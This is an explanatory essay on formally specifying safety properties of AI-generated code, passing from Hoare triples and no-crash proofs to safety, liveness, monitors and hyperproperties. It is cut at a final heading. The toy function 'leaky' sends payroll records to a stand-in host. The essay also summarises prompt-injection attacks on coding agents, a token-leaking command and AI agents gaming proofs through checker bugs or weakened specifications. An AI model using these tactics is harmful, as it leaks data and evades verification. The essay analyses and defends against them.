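# Which safety properties of AI-generated code can be formally specified

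## What a formal specification says about a program

Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that a program meets its specification, which is a mathematical statement of what the program must or must not do. A person or a machine can check the program against this statement. Testing tries a program on a sample of inputs, while a proof covers every input, but it establishes only what the specification requires.

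Most specifications define what a program should return, but not where it sends data, how long it runs or what else it changes. A program can therefore meet its specification and still exfiltrate data, leak information through side channels, abuse resources or have unintended effects. This matters more as AI systems write more code, because the people who run the code have often not read it closely.

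### Models, traces and proofs

A payroll function might take a list of employee records, each with a public department and a secret salary, and return the average salary in each department. If employee i works in department dᵢ and earns sᵢ, the right answer for department d is the sum of sᵢ over everyone with dᵢ = d, divided by the number of such people.

Proving anything about this function requires a program model, a mathematical description of what the instructions of the programming language do. A typical model treats execution as a series of states. Each state holds the current value of every variable, and a rule for each instruction fixes how one state leads to the next. A trace is the sequence of states or events in one run. With two engineers on the payroll, a trace might start with all totals at zero, pass through running totals of 70,000 and 160,000, and end as the function returns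 80,000. "Returns the right averages" then becomes a condition on traces: every trace that starts from a list of records and comes to an end must end with the averages for that list. The usual name for a condition of this kind, which ties outputs to inputs, is functional correctness. (Some requirements, the hyperproperties, need several traces side by side.)

A trace contains only what the formal model records, so the choice of model limits which properties a specification can express. If the states hold only variables, a function that also posts the salaries to a website has the same traces as one that doesn't, except perhaps for an extra step in which no variable changes. No specification over those traces can distinguish the two functions.

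A proof here is a chain of logical steps from the model to the conclusion that all the program's traces meet the specification. People make mistakes in long proofs, so verification projects write them in a formal language and run them through a proof checker, a program that tests each step against fixed rules of logic. Isabelle/HOL and Lean are two widely used systems built around such a checker, which their developers call the kernel. Checking a proof is mechanical, even though finding one can take years.

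### Accepting code from a stranger

*Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) showed how this difference lets a computer's owner run machine code from an untrusted author. The owner publishes a safety policy, which contains rules for when a program may perform each operation and an interface that lists what holds when the owner's computer, the host, calls the code and what must hold when the code returns. The author compiles a program and attaches a proof that it obeys the policy. The host then steps through the machine code and computes a logical formula, the verification condition, which guarantees that the program obeys the policy if the formula is true. For a load from memory, for example, the host adds the requirement that the program may read that address. A checker then confirms that the attached proof proves the formula. Because the host computes the formula itself, the author cannot substitute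 a proof of something easier.

The owner has to trust the policy and the host's checking software, and Necula's logic is simple enough that a naive checker for its rules takes a couple of pages of code. The owner doesn't have to trust whoever wrote the program, the compiler or the tool that found the proof. Tampering with the package in transit either breaks the proof, so the host rejects it, or produces a different program that also obeys the policy. The scheme was also practical. Necula's hand-written network filters, each with its proof, ran ten times faster than equivalent filters in the interpreted language that operating systems used for safety.

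Necula's main example is a function that adds up the integers in a list. The policy requires the function to read only valid memory and, if it stops, to leave an integer in the result register. A function that returned 0 for every list would pass the same check. The policy is meant to protect the memory of the surrounding system, and it does, so this is not a flaw in the method. But a reader who saw the word "proved" next to a function named "sum" could easily think the function had been proved to add correctly.

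A proof's trusted base is everything it assumes without proving: the proof checker, the compiler (unless someone has verified its output), the runtime system, the hardware model and the specification itself. seL4 is a small operating-system kernel whose developers proved it correct down to its C code and, on some processors, down to the binary. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* describes its full trusted base. The proofs still assume that about 340 lines of assembly on ARM processors and some 1,200 lines of start-up code are correct, and that the hardware works as the model describes. The proof that secrets do not leak holds only for the channels in the model, which does not cover timing.

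The seL4 developers tell readers to worry about these assumptions rather than about the proof checker. That is good advice when whoever wrote the proof wanted it to be valid. On July 25, 2026, someone published a Lean "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous problem about whole numbers. Lean's kernel accepted it, and so did Nanoda, an independent checker, as the security project Openwall (2026) reported. The proof exploited a kernel bug that made it possible to prove any statement. According to the release note for the fix, the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2 (2026-07-28)* (2026), a single proof can exploit both this bug and an unrelated one in Nanoda. More fixes followed in August. An OpenAI agent had used another kernel bug to produce two false proofs, both of which Nanoda caught, according to the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.1 (2026-08-21)* (2026). Kernels are small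 and their developers fix such bugs quickly, so there is still a good case for relying on checked proofs, but it is weaker for anyone who runs a single checker on proofs from a source that is looking for bugs to exploit.

### Careless, steered and hostile authors

The volume of AI-generated code strains review. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) followed 802 developers at a company that had set out to double its output with AI. By the end of the study, about 90% of its pull requests (proposed changes to the code) were labeled as AI-authored. Each reviewer handled roughly twice as many as before, and the human review that remained was increasingly approval without comment. The share of changes that developers later reverted stayed flat, which is some evidence that the faults people notice did not become more common.

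Donaldson (2026), in *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back*, points out that nobody needs to trust a language model's proof, because a checker will reject a bad one and a wrong guess only wastes time and computing power. But no checker can catch a mistake in the specification. How much the specification must rule out depends on what kind of author wrote the code.

Some code is vulnerable only because its author was careless. *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (Livshits, 2026) cites a study in which language models produced vulnerable code at rates between 9.8% and 42.1%, though newer models may well do better. Missing bounds checks and unsanitised inputs are familiar mistakes, and a list of such mistakes is very useful for checking code whose author is not trying to hide anything.

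Coding agents can also write bad code because they follow instructions that outsiders have planted in bug reports, comments and configuration files. *Package Hallucination Attacks on Coding Agents through Prompt Injection in Rule Files* (2026) describes an attack that hides text in a file of coding rules, so that the agent imports a malicious package whenever a task would normally call for a particular legitimate one. Nakibly and Babo (2026), in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, searched about 143 million issues, pull requests and comments on the code-hosting site GitHub and found 43 real attacks in text that the site does not display. When they replayed the attacks against five models, one small model carried out 19% of them. Such attacks are rare and, for now, mostly ineffective, but a successful one in effect lets the attacker decide what code the agent writes.

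An AI agent may also work against the check itself. Philipp (2026), in *Zero-Trust Formal Methods*, describes a system in which AI agents write all the code and proofs, and assumes that any of them may game its objective. Such an agent might weaken a specification until it is trivial, tell the verifier to assume a false statement (from which anything can be proved), or exploit a bug in the checker. The design must hold even if the agents behave like an adversary rewarded for passing, though Philipp does not assume that they mean harm. *Validating a Lean Proof*, in the Lean Language Reference, likewise treats unreviewed AI-generated proofs and programs as malicious.

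A specification protects against a careless author if the programs that such an author would plausibly write, and that meet the specification, are harmless. A hostile author can pick any program that meets the specification, so all of them must be harmless, including those a careless author would never write. Suppose the payroll specification allows each average to be off by half a cent in either direction, to allow for rounding, and the function reports six decimal places. Each average then has about 10,000 permitted values. A careless programmer's rounding errors carry no message, but a hostile programmer can choose values whose last four digits encode part of somebody's salary, and the function still meets its specification.

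### Lampson's channels and the four harms

In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) posed the problem in this strong form by asking how a customer can give confidential input to somebody else's service program and be sure that the program does not pass it to its owner. He wanted a method that would confine "an arbitrary program", and accepted that some programs would work only when unconfined. He also saw that leaks are worse than errors in one respect, because wrong answers leave the customer with evidence, while a leak generally leaves no sign. A flat rate of reverted changes is therefore weak evidence that nothing has leaked.

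Lampson listed ways the data could leak and sorted these channels into three kinds. Storage channels are places that the service can write and an outsider can read, such as a file in the owner's directory. A less obvious storage channel exists where a system forbids two programs to open the same file at once, because the service can signal one bit at a time by opening and closing the file. Legitimate channels are outputs that the service is supposed to produce, such as the bill for its work, which is Lampson's example, or the payroll function's spare decimal places. Covert channels are things that nobody intended to carry information, such as the load on the machine. (Later writers often use "covert" for storage channels as well.) Lampson doubted that anyone could rigorously identify every channel in a system of even moderate complexity, so whoever decides what goes into a trace may leave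 some out.

Exfiltration means that code sends data, by a route that ordinarily carries data, to someone who should not have it. In one attack that Nakibly and Babo found, hidden text in a bug report to Google's Gemini CLI project instructed the project's agent to run a shell command. The command would copy the repository's access token, in disguised form, to a place from which a later step might print it. The payroll function could exfiltrate data by writing every salary to a file that an outsider can read, and then returning the right averages.

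Code leaks secrets through a side channel when they can be learned from how it runs rather than from its output. In Lampson's example, a service sends a message by deliberately varying its ratio of computing to input and output, and another program on the same machine reads the message from the changes in performance. Careless code can leak secrets this way by accident. If a payroll function pauses one millisecond for every thousand in the director's salary, anyone who can time the pause can work out the salary.

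A program abuses resources if it uses far more time, memory or other capacity than its task warrants. Until August 2026, when the Lean Language Reference announced a size limit on numerals, a hostile input could make Lean's kernel use unbounded memory and time building enormous ones. The payroll function might return the correct averages but try every possible order of the records before adding them up. For 20 employees, that is about 2.4 × 10¹⁸ orders, which would take about 77 years at a billion per second.

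Unintended effects are changes to anything outside the task. *Trojan Horse*, a 2026 study of poisoned code repositories, includes an attack in which an agent working on a legitimate development task irreversibly deletes critical repository data. In the payroll function, an extra line that raises one employee's salary in the database after the averages are computed would also be an unintended effect. The four categories overlap somewhat, since writing the salaries to a file is both an unintended effect and exfiltration.

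### Expressible, checkable, adequate

Whether a specification can exclude one of these harms depends on the answers to three questions, and a favorable answer to one does not guarantee favorable answers to the others.

A property is expressible if someone can state it formally in some model. "Opens no network connection" is easy to state in a model that records connections, but "does nothing that its users would object to" is harder. *Reliable Software and Security Engineering with Unreliable Tools* (Khachaturov, 2026) classes security against unknown attacks as difficult or impossible to formalise.

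A property is checkable if someone can show that a given program has it. Donaldson notes that most interesting verification problems are undecidable for software with unbounded memory, which means that no algorithm gives the right answer for every program. Proof-carrying code works around this limit by requiring the code's author to supply a proof before the code can run. This reduces usefulness but not safety, because some harmless programs cannot run when nobody finds a proof for them, much as some would stop working under Lampson's confinement.

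A formal specification is adequate if it captures what people meant by it. A ban on network connections can be expressed formally and, in a suitable language, checked easily, but a payroll function can obey it and still leak salaries by writing them to a shared file. No proof checker can establish adequacy, because that requires comparing the specification with someone's intention, which may itself need more thought. For example, the requirement "Keep individual salaries secret and return the average for each department" cannot be met when a department has only one employee, because the average is that person's salary.

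## What correctness and no-crash proofs leave out

### The Hoare triple

Most proofs of functional correctness use some version of a notation that the computer scientist Tony Hoare published in 1969. A Hoare triple, now usually written {P} C {Q}, consists of a precondition P, a program C and a postcondition Q. The triple holds if, whenever C starts in a state where P is true and eventually stops, Q is true in the final state. For example, {x = 3} x := x + 1 {x = 4} holds. A triple defined this way expresses partial correctness. Total correctness also requires C to stop.

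The precondition, P, states what the caller must guarantee. Binary search, which finds an item in a list by repeatedly halving it, works only on sorted lists, so "the list is sorted" belongs in P. The triple then allows the program to do anything with an unsorted list. A precondition that is never true makes every program correct. Postconditions can also be weak. Computer Things' *Three ways formally verified code can go wrong in practice* (2025) treats even a type signature as a specification. If the signature of a function called "inc" requires only that it turn an integer into an integer, the function is correct by that specification even when it subtracts one.

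For the payroll function, let the records at the start be (d₁, s₁), …, (dₙ, sₙ), where dᵢ is a department and sᵢ a salary. A reasonable specification is:

- P: every sᵢ is a non-negative whole number.
- Q: the result has exactly one entry for each department in the records, and for each such department d, result[d] = (sum of sᵢ over all i with dᵢ = d) ÷ (number of i with dᵢ = d).

Q must refer to the records as they were at the start. Otherwise a program could empty the list, return an empty result and satisfy Q.

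### Three payroll programs

All three of these programs satisfy the triple, and they satisfy it in the strict sense of total correctness:

```
def honest(records):
    total, count = {}, {}
    for dept, salary in records:
        total[dept] = total.get(dept, 0) + salary
        count[dept] = count.get(dept, 0) + 1
    return {dept: Fraction(total[dept], count[dept]) for dept in total}

def leaky(records):
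    send("collector.example", records)
    return honest(records)

def slow(records):
    for i in range(10**15):
        pass
    return honest(records)
```

The proof for "honest" needs a loop invariant, a statement that is true before the loop starts and that each pass through the loop keeps true. Here it is that after k records, total[d] is the sum of the salaries in department d among those k records, and count[d] is the number of those salaries. This is true before the loop because k is 0 and there is nothing to add up. Each pass keeps it true by taking in one more record and updating one sum and one count. When k reaches n, dividing the sums by the counts gives Q.

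"leaky" sends every salary to a stranger's computer and then does the same work as "honest". Hoare's rule for running one piece of code after another says that if {P} C₁ {R} and {R} C₂ {Q} both hold, then {P} C₁; C₂ {Q} holds. In a model whose states contain only the program's variables, "send" changes nothing, so {P} send {P} holds. Combining this with the triple for "honest" gives the triple for "leaky". The proof for "leaky" is the proof for "honest" with a line added, and every step is valid.

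Adding network traffic to the states would not be enough to stop this, because Q would still have to restrict the traffic. Slides from the developers of Lean illustrate this with a toy language in which a postcondition is a condition on the list of input and output events so far, the memory and the local variables. The sample specification requires that memory be unchanged, that the list contain exactly one event (the input of some value v), and that the variable "a" end up holding v. A program that also output v would fail, because the list would contain two events. If someone deleted the clause about events from the specification, the same program would pass, even though the model still records its output. The payroll specification can be fixed by recording events and adding "the list of events is empty" to Q.

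That repair catches "leaky" but not "slow", which counts to 10¹⁵ before it starts. At a billion steps per second, that takes about eleven and a half days. A Hoare triple relates the starting state to the final state, and neither contains the number of steps between them. Total correctness requires only that this number be finite. Under partial correctness, even a program that loops forever passes, because it never reaches a final state in which to evaluate Q. The function that pauses longer when the director earns more satisfies the triple for the same reason as "slow", and the one that raises somebody's salary in the database satisfies it for the same reason as "leaky". A single sensible specification therefore admits examples of all four harms.

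### lean-zip: a missing theorem and a false assumption

How much these gaps matter for real verified code is partly an empirical question, and lean-zip is a good test case. It is a version of zlib, the widely used C library for compressing data, that ten AI agents wrote in Lean and proved correct on their own. One of its main theorems covers every byte array smaller than one gigabyte and every compression level:

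decompress(compress(data, level)) = data

The version in the Lean slides replaces the gigabyte limit with a maximum output size that the caller chooses.

This round-trip theorem is a strong guarantee for someone who compresses a file and wants it back. But it covers decompression only when the input came from lean-zip's own compressor, and an attacker crafting a malicious file has no reason to use that compressor. The equation alone would also hold for two functions that return their input unchanged, though lean-zip has further proofs about the compressed format and its checksums.

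*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, a post on kirancodes.me, describes an attack on the library by fuzzing, which means running a program on huge numbers of generated inputs, many of them malformed. The blogger removed the theorems, the documentation and the optional links to the original C library, then had Claude, Anthropic's AI model, run the attack without knowing that the code had been verified, so that it would not give up early. Claude ran 16 fuzzers in parallel for about 19 hours on the compressor and on ZIP, gzip, tar and raw compressed data. It also wrote 48 exploit files by hand, modelled on known zlib vulnerabilities. Other tools checked for invalid memory accesses and undefined behavior.

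After 105,823,818 executions, Claude had found no memory errors in the verified code, such as buffer overflows, use of memory after its release or reads outside an array. The theorems do not fully explain this. Most of the fuzzers fed in malformed files, to which the round-trip theorem does not apply, and Claude credited much of the result to Lean's type system. The result is still impressive because C programs that do this job have often had such bugs.

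Claude did find two bugs elsewhere. One was a denial of service in the archive parser, which reads ZIP file headers. A ZIP header lists the size of each compressed file, and the parser requested that much memory without comparing the number to the actual size of the archive. A 156-byte file with a listed size of several exabytes made the program run out of memory and crash. The standard "unzip" program checks the listed size before requesting memory.

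The other bug was a heap buffer overflow, in which a program writes past the end of a block of memory it has reserved. It was in the Lean runtime, the C++ code that compiled Lean programs rely on for basic jobs such as reserving memory. To hold n bytes, the runtime reserved n + 24, using the extra 24 for bookkeeping. Computers usually store such numbers in 64 bits, so counting restarts from zero at 2⁶⁴. If n was 2⁶⁴ − 1, the runtime therefore reserved only 23 bytes, but let the caller read up to 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes into them. Another 156-byte ZIP file was enough to trigger the bug, which affected every version of Lean 4 up to the test version of April 11, 2026. A fix was pending when the blogger wrote.

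The denial of service came from a missing specification, since the archive parser had no theorems at all. The remedy is to state and prove that the parser never requests more bytes than the archive contains. The heap overflow happened because Lean proofs assume that the runtime handles byte arrays as the logic describes, and here it did not. In terms of the triple, the problem was in C rather than in P or Q, because the program the computer ran differed slightly from the one in the proof. More theorems about lean-zip would not have fixed this. The repair had to be made in the runtime, which is part of the trusted base of every Lean program.

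The distinction between a wrong property and a wrong assumption is useful but not always sharp. As Computer Things notes, well-known proofs of binary search used integers of unlimited size, while many programming languages use integers that can overflow, and this mismatch could be called either. The denial of service also has elements of both. A proof that the parser extracts every valid archive correctly might well have succeeded without the size check if it assumed, as most such proofs do, that memory never runs out. The two bugs were also connected, because the missing check let a number from an attacker's file reach the faulty runtime function.

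### Proofs that 239 programs never crash

lean-zip's agents wrote new code with proof in mind. Most software already exists, in languages such as C, and comes with no specification. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), published on October 22, describes how Anthropic and the formal-methods company Theorem took a specification from something that many projects already had. OSS-Fuzz, a Google service, continually fuzzes open-source libraries, and for this the libraries have fuzz harnesses, which are small programs that take a string of bytes and use it to call some of a library's functions. A fuzzer runs a harness on many inputs to see whether it crashes. Anthropic and Theorem turned "this harness does not crash" into a theorem about all inputs up to a given size.

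In *Pre-QED* (Lim, Tu and colleagues, 2026), the pipeline compiles the library and its harness into one program for RISC-V, an open processor design. The compiler adds checks that crash the program when it accesses memory it shouldn't or does something the C language leaves undefined, since these errors might otherwise go unnoticed. Software then generates the entire theorem by combining the program with formal models of the processor and Linux. Claude writes a proof in Rocq, a system similar to Lean, and Rocq's kernel checks it. If Claude finds a real bug, it patches the library, and the pipeline generates a new theorem for the patched program.

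The results cover 239 harnesses, or entry points, in 123 libraries. The title of Smith's *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (2026) gives the total length of the proofs. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), a Russian news report, says that a typical proof has about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 instructions.

The theorem is that for any input smaller than 64 MB, any memory layout and any response the modelled operating system might give, the program exits normally without violating memory safety or failing an assertion. An assertion is a check that programmers write into the code, and some harnesses contain demanding ones. For example, a harness might compress its input, decompress the result and assert that the output matches the original, so a proof that it never crashes also proves that decompression recovers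 the input. Most harnesses have less demanding assertions. A library whose functions all returned immediately without doing anything would never crash, so Claude had an easy way to cheat when patching. To discourage this, the pipeline penalized patches and gave extra credit for proving which inputs a patch affected, and people audited the patches.

As for the four harms:

- **Exfiltration.** The theorem puts no condition on what the program sends or where. A harness around "leaky" would exit normally after posting the salaries. (If the Linux model left out network calls, a proof about "leaky" might be impossible, but only by accident.)
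- **Side channels.** There is no condition on timing either, and no comparison between runs with different secrets.
- **Resource abuse.** Here the theorem does help. It rules out infinite loops, and EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) notes that the model gives each program a fixed memory budget. But "exits normally" includes exiting after eleven days, so "slow" passes.
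- **Unintended effects.** The theorem excludes corruption of the program's own memory. It excludes changes to files or databases only if an assertion in the harness happens to check for them.

Even a proof that a "verified library" never crashes may cover only the sequence of calls in its harness. Lim and colleagues illustrate this with a small library for reading a stream of data in pieces. Its harness opens a stream, reads once and closes it, and a proof shows that this sequence never crashes. But the library limits each read to the total length of the stream instead of the length that remains. If a program reads 40 bytes from a 64-byte stream and then asks for 40 more, the library copies 16 bytes from beyond the end. This is a serious bug in a library meant for reading in pieces, but the proof doesn't rule it out because the harness never reads twice.

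The example is artificial, but the gap it illustrates is common. In 29 of the libraries with published proofs, the harnesses call on average 22.1% of the functions that the library offers to other programs. The figure is 6.5% for cJSON, a library for a common data format, and 0.7% for the web cache Varnish. These percentages probably understate the proofs' coverage somewhat, since one call to a parser can run much internal code that the count leaves out. But even a harness that calls every function may call them in only one order. Lim and colleagues built alternative harnesses that turn their input into an arbitrary sequence of permitted calls, and these reach 89.3% of the functions on average. They published these harnesses as challenges, which are harder to prove because the library's internal state carries over from one call to the next and the sequences can be arbitrarily long.

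The models also cover only single-threaded programs with no dynamically loaded parts, and they assume that the hardware behaves as specified. Most people compile these libraries without the extra checks and run them on other kinds of processor, so they must trust that the result still holds.

Some bugs don't cause crashes. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (December 2, 2026) concerns logic bugs, in which software breaks the unwritten rules of how it should work. For example, a login function might accept an expired password. Such bugs rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect, and a no-crash theorem based on a fuzz harness has the same limitation. Proving that code obeys one of these rules requires writing the rule down first.

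### Code that passes its tests and is still insecure

*CWEVAL* (Peng, Cui and colleagues, 2025) measures how often code does what was asked but is still insecure. Its benchmark has 119 programming tasks in five languages and covers 31 entries in the Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalogue of software weaknesses. Each task has one set of tests for function and another for security. The researchers checked that every task has a solution that passes both sets and an insecure one that passes only the functional tests. They kept any hint about security out of the instructions because people who ask for code often give none.

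In *Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation*, Al Mamun and Uddin (2026) ran the benchmark in October on four open-weight models with plain prompts. Of the samples that passed the functional tests, 29.2% failed the security tests. The benchmark uses tasks where an insecure solution is easy to write, so this figure is not an estimate for code in general. Passing the functional tests also does not prove that the code is correct. Claude Sonnet 5.5 passed both sets of tests 92.1% of the time with a method that supplies relevant catalogue entries and repairs the code after testing.

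For the question of what can be specified, the kind of failure matters more than the rate. Peng and colleagues' security tests observe four kinds of thing, and each puts a different demand on a specification:

| What the test observes | Example | What a specification needs to catch it |
|---|---|---|
| The returned value | A line break hidden in a web header | A stronger postcondition on the result |
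| Memory accesses | Reading past the end of an array in C | A model in which an invalid access is an error |
| Data outside the function | A database query that an attacker's input has altered | The database in the model, and a postcondition about it |
| Running time | An input that keeps the function busy past a time limit | A count of steps in the model, and a bound on it |

A fuller functional specification would catch the failures in the first row. In one task, the function must store a user's value in a web response header. Headers are separated by line breaks, so a user who can include a line break in the value can add more headers. One of the models, Qwen3-Coder-30B, omitted the check for line breaks in all five of its attempts. An ordinary postcondition can require that the stored value contain no line breaks, whatever the user supplies. A similar postcondition would work for another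 task, in which the function writes a user's message to a log.

A proof of functional correctness for C code normally rules out memory errors, even though they don't reliably show up in a return value. A C program that reads outside an array has no defined result, so nobody can prove it correct. As with the salary-raising payroll function, a specification can rule out altered database queries only if it covers the database, not just return values. It must also require that everything the code isn't supposed to change stay the same, which is called a frame condition.

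No condition on a program's result, however detailed, can rule out slow running, so the specification also has to cover running time.

Even in the first row, "could catch" depends on somebody thinking of the condition, and the header task does not mention line breaks. When Al Mamun and Uddin searched the catalogue using only the text of each task, the relevant weakness was among the top five results 47.1% of the time. Their full method, in which a model first drafts a plausible insecure solution and searches with that as well, raised this to 89.1%. AI can therefore help find missing conditions, but it can also make them too strict. When the same Qwen model received catalogue entries without the rest of the method, its code blocked line breaks in the header but also rejected ordinary lists of languages, such as "en-US, en;q=0.9". A security postcondition needs to be paired with a functional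 one, because a function that rejects every input could satisfy the security postcondition alone.

### What proofs over all inputs achieve

Functional correctness still matters for security because many vulnerabilities are functional errors on inputs that nobody tried. Testers mostly choose inputs that users might send, while attackers look for the rare one that breaks something, and a proof covers both. If the header function's precondition allows any string, and a proof shows that the value it stores never contains a line break, then no attack that relies on a line break in that value will work, including attacks nobody has invented yet.

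Experience with verified code supports this. Claude found hundreds of bugs while working on the 123 libraries, some of which appear only with inputs of tens of megabytes, which a fuzzer is unlikely to try. OpenNET mentions a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used parser. The blogger who attacked lean-zip found bugs only in code the proofs didn't cover, and compares this with a 2011 study of compilers. In that study, random testing found no bugs in the verified optimization passes of CompCert, a C compiler, but did find some in an unverified part.

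The main objection to formal verification used to be the labor it required, but that objection is now much weaker. The seL4 kernel took about two person-years to build and twenty to verify, according to Lim and colleagues, whereas EconoTimes reports that the work on the 123 libraries took a few weeks. The comparison overstates the newer project's advantage, since seL4's proofs establish far more than the absence of crashes. But OpenNET reports that the newer project also proved richer properties, including that the Linux kernel's version of zlib conforms to the published standard for the format.

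No-crash proofs give some protection against exfiltration. An outsider who wants to steal data from a server often starts by exploiting a memory error, because writing past the end of a buffer can make the server run the outsider's own instructions. Proving memory safety rules out this attack and any harm that would follow from it. For a library written by honest people, this may be most of what its users need. It does not help against a hostile author, because the program already runs the instructions that the author chose.

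## Properties of one run and properties that compare runs

A Hoare triple is a condition that each run of a program must meet on its own. Many security rules have this form, but secrecy doesn't. Checking whether the payroll function's output depends on the director's salary requires comparing one run with another in which the salary is different. A rule that compares runs needs other methods of checking, and a program can break it merely by filling in a detail that the specification left open.

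### Safety and liveness

In *Defining Liveness*, Alpern and Schneider (1985) treat a trace as an infinite sequence of states. If a program stops, its trace repeats the final state forever. A property of single traces is the set of acceptable traces, and a program has the property if all its traces are in that set.

Informally, a safety property requires that something bad never happens, which is a narrower meaning than "safety" has in everyday use. Formally, a set P of traces is a safety property if every trace outside P has a finite beginning that no trace in P has. Once a run has produced that beginning, nothing it does later can make the run acceptable. "Never sends data to an unlisted host" is a safety property because no later step can undo a send. Partial correctness is also a safety property, where the bad thing is stopping with a wrong result.

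A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens. Formally, P is a liveness property if every finite sequence of states can be extended to a trace in P, so no finite sequence can show that P has been violated. Termination is the standard example. A program that has run for a year might still stop at the next step.

"Eventually stops" is a liveness property, and the payroll function that first counts to 10¹⁵ satisfies it. "Stops within a billion steps" is a safety property, because a run that is still going after a billion steps has permanently violated it. Someone worried about resource abuse wants the bound. The proofs also differ, since a safety proof uses an invariant, like the one for the loop in "honest", while a liveness proof usually needs a quantity that keeps falling but can't fall forever, such as the number of records still to process.

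Total correctness combines a safety property, partial correctness, with a liveness property, termination. Alpern and Schneider proved that every property of single traces is likewise the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. Their proof uses topology, but there is a short direct argument. Let P be any set of traces.

- Let S be the set of traces whose every finite beginning is also the beginning of some trace in P. S contains P. It is a safety property, because a trace outside S has a beginning that no trace in P has, and any other trace with that beginning is outside S too.
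- Let L contain every trace in P and every trace outside S. To see that L is a liveness property, take any finite sequence of states. If some trace in P starts with it, that trace is in L. If none does, all traces that start with it are outside S, and so they are in L.
- A trace that is in both S and L must be in P, because the only other traces in L are outside S. So P is the intersection of S and L.

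If P is "stops with the right averages", then S is "never stops with wrong averages" and L is "stops".

### What a monitor can enforce

The owner of a computer can use a monitor instead of proving something about all runs in advance. A monitor watches each run as it happens and steps in when the program is about to break a rule. Firewalls and the access checks in operating systems are monitors. Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, proved that if a monitor can only halt the program, every rule it can enforce is a safety property.

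The monitor observes only the current run, so the rule has to be a condition on single traces. The monitor can't observe future steps, so it can't let a run pass through an unacceptable stage that later steps might correct, since the program might stop there. If it rejects a run, it has to do so after finitely many steps. A rule that meets all three conditions is a safety property.

Schneider's example is a rule against sending any message after reading a file. The monitor needs one bit of memory to record whether the program has read a file. It allows every action until the first read, and after that it halts the program at any attempt to send.

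A monitor that can only halt the program still can't enforce some safety properties. One is the rule that nobody may wait more than a fixed number of seconds for a resource. This is a safety property because the limit is exceeded at a definite moment, but halting the program can't prevent that, since time keeps passing. If the rule counts the program's execution steps instead of seconds, a monitor can enforce it.

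Schneider also warns that the file rule has its intended meaning only if the definition of "send" covers every way of sending a message, including obscure ones. Lampson had the same concern about overlooked channels, and it applies equally to a proof.

Real monitors often do more than halt programs. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005), studied monitors that can also suppress or insert actions. One of their examples is the liveness property that a program which does anything at all must eventually write an audit entry. A monitor that can only halt the program would have to stop it at its first action, because there is no audit entry yet. An editing monitor can hold the actions back while reporting to the program that they succeeded, then release them all when the program writes the audit entry. If it never does, none of the actions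 take effect, which the rule allows. Databases handle transactions in much the same way.

Monitors of this kind can enforce what Ligatti and colleagues call infinite renewal properties, as long as an algorithm can tell which finite runs are acceptable and doing nothing is acceptable. In a renewal property, an infinite run is acceptable exactly when infinitely many of its finite beginnings are. The class includes every safety property and some liveness properties, but not termination. This helps prevent unintended effects, because a monitor can hold back a batch of database changes until the batch is complete and harmless.

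Editing helps less with exfiltration. As Ligatti and colleagues point out, a monitor can't simulate sending an email, wait for the program to react to the reply, and then cancel the email. An editing monitor also sees only one run at a time, so it can't compare that run with others.

### Why secrecy is not a property of single runs

Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, gave a general definition for rules that can't be checked one run at a time. A hyperproperty is a set of sets of traces. A program satisfies the hyperproperty H if T, the set of all the program's traces, is one of the sets in H. H therefore lists the acceptable programs rather than the acceptable runs. Every property P of single traces has an equivalent hyperproperty, the set of all subsets of P.

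Hyperproperties also cover rules unrelated to secrecy. Suppose a service must keep its mean response time below one second over all its runs. Whether a run that takes three seconds is acceptable depends on how fast the other runs are.

"The output does not depend on the secret" is a hyperproperty that no set of acceptable traces can express. To prove this, let the secret h be a single bit, perhaps 1 if the director earns more than 100,000 and 0 otherwise, and consider two harmless programs and a leaky one:

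```
def zero(h): return 0
def one(h):  return 1
def leak(h): return h
```

Each trace can be written as a pair (h, output). If some set P of traces expressed the rule, a program would keep the secret exactly when all its traces were in P. "zero" keeps the secret, so P would have to contain (0, 0) and (1, 0). "one" keeps it too, so P would also have to contain (0, 1) and (1, 1). The traces of "leak" are (0, 0) and (1, 1), which are both in P, so "leak" would count as keeping the secret. But "leak" returns the secret, so no such P exists.

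Each run of "leak" looks exactly like a run of a harmless program. The leak is in the correlation between runs, so even a monitor that records everything about one run can't detect it.

### Two readings of "no exfiltration"

People who ask for code that doesn't exfiltrate data could mean either of two things. One is that the program never sends anything to a host that is not on an approved list. The other is that no secret influences what the program sends. The host rule is a safety property of single traces, and a firewall can enforce it. The secrecy rule compares runs. It is a form of noninterference, which has a fuller definition in the next section. The two rules disagree about quite ordinary programs:

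| What the payroll function sends | Host rule | Secrecy rule |
|---|---|---|
| Every salary, to an unlisted host | Forbids | Forbids |
| Every salary, to an attacker's account on a listed code-hosting site | Allows | Forbids |
| Product plans that nobody marked as secret, to an unlisted host | Forbids | Allows |
| Department averages, to the company's own listed accounting system | Allows | Forbids |

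The host rule doesn't restrict what a program sends, so the program can leak data through any listed host that accepts data from the public, such as a code-hosting site. It can even leak a bit by choosing which of two listed hosts to contact. The secrecy rule applies regardless of destination, but it protects only what someone has classified as secret. It is also too strict for much useful work. For example, it forbids reporting an average salary, because the average depends on the individual salaries. A specification can require both rules, which would block the behavior in the first three rows, but it would also block the legitimate behavior in the fourth unless it made an exception for averages.

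Monitors can't enforce the secrecy rule itself, so those meant to prevent leaks enforce a stricter rule, as Schneider notes. His rule against sending after reading a file can serve this purpose. If secrets reach the program only through files, whatever it sends before opening one can't depend on them. But the monitor would also halt a payroll function that read the records and then tried to send a message saying only "done". Whether this restriction is acceptable depends on the program. For a function that has no reason to use the network, a ban on all sending blocks nothing useful and is much easier to check than secrecy.

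### Checking two runs as one program

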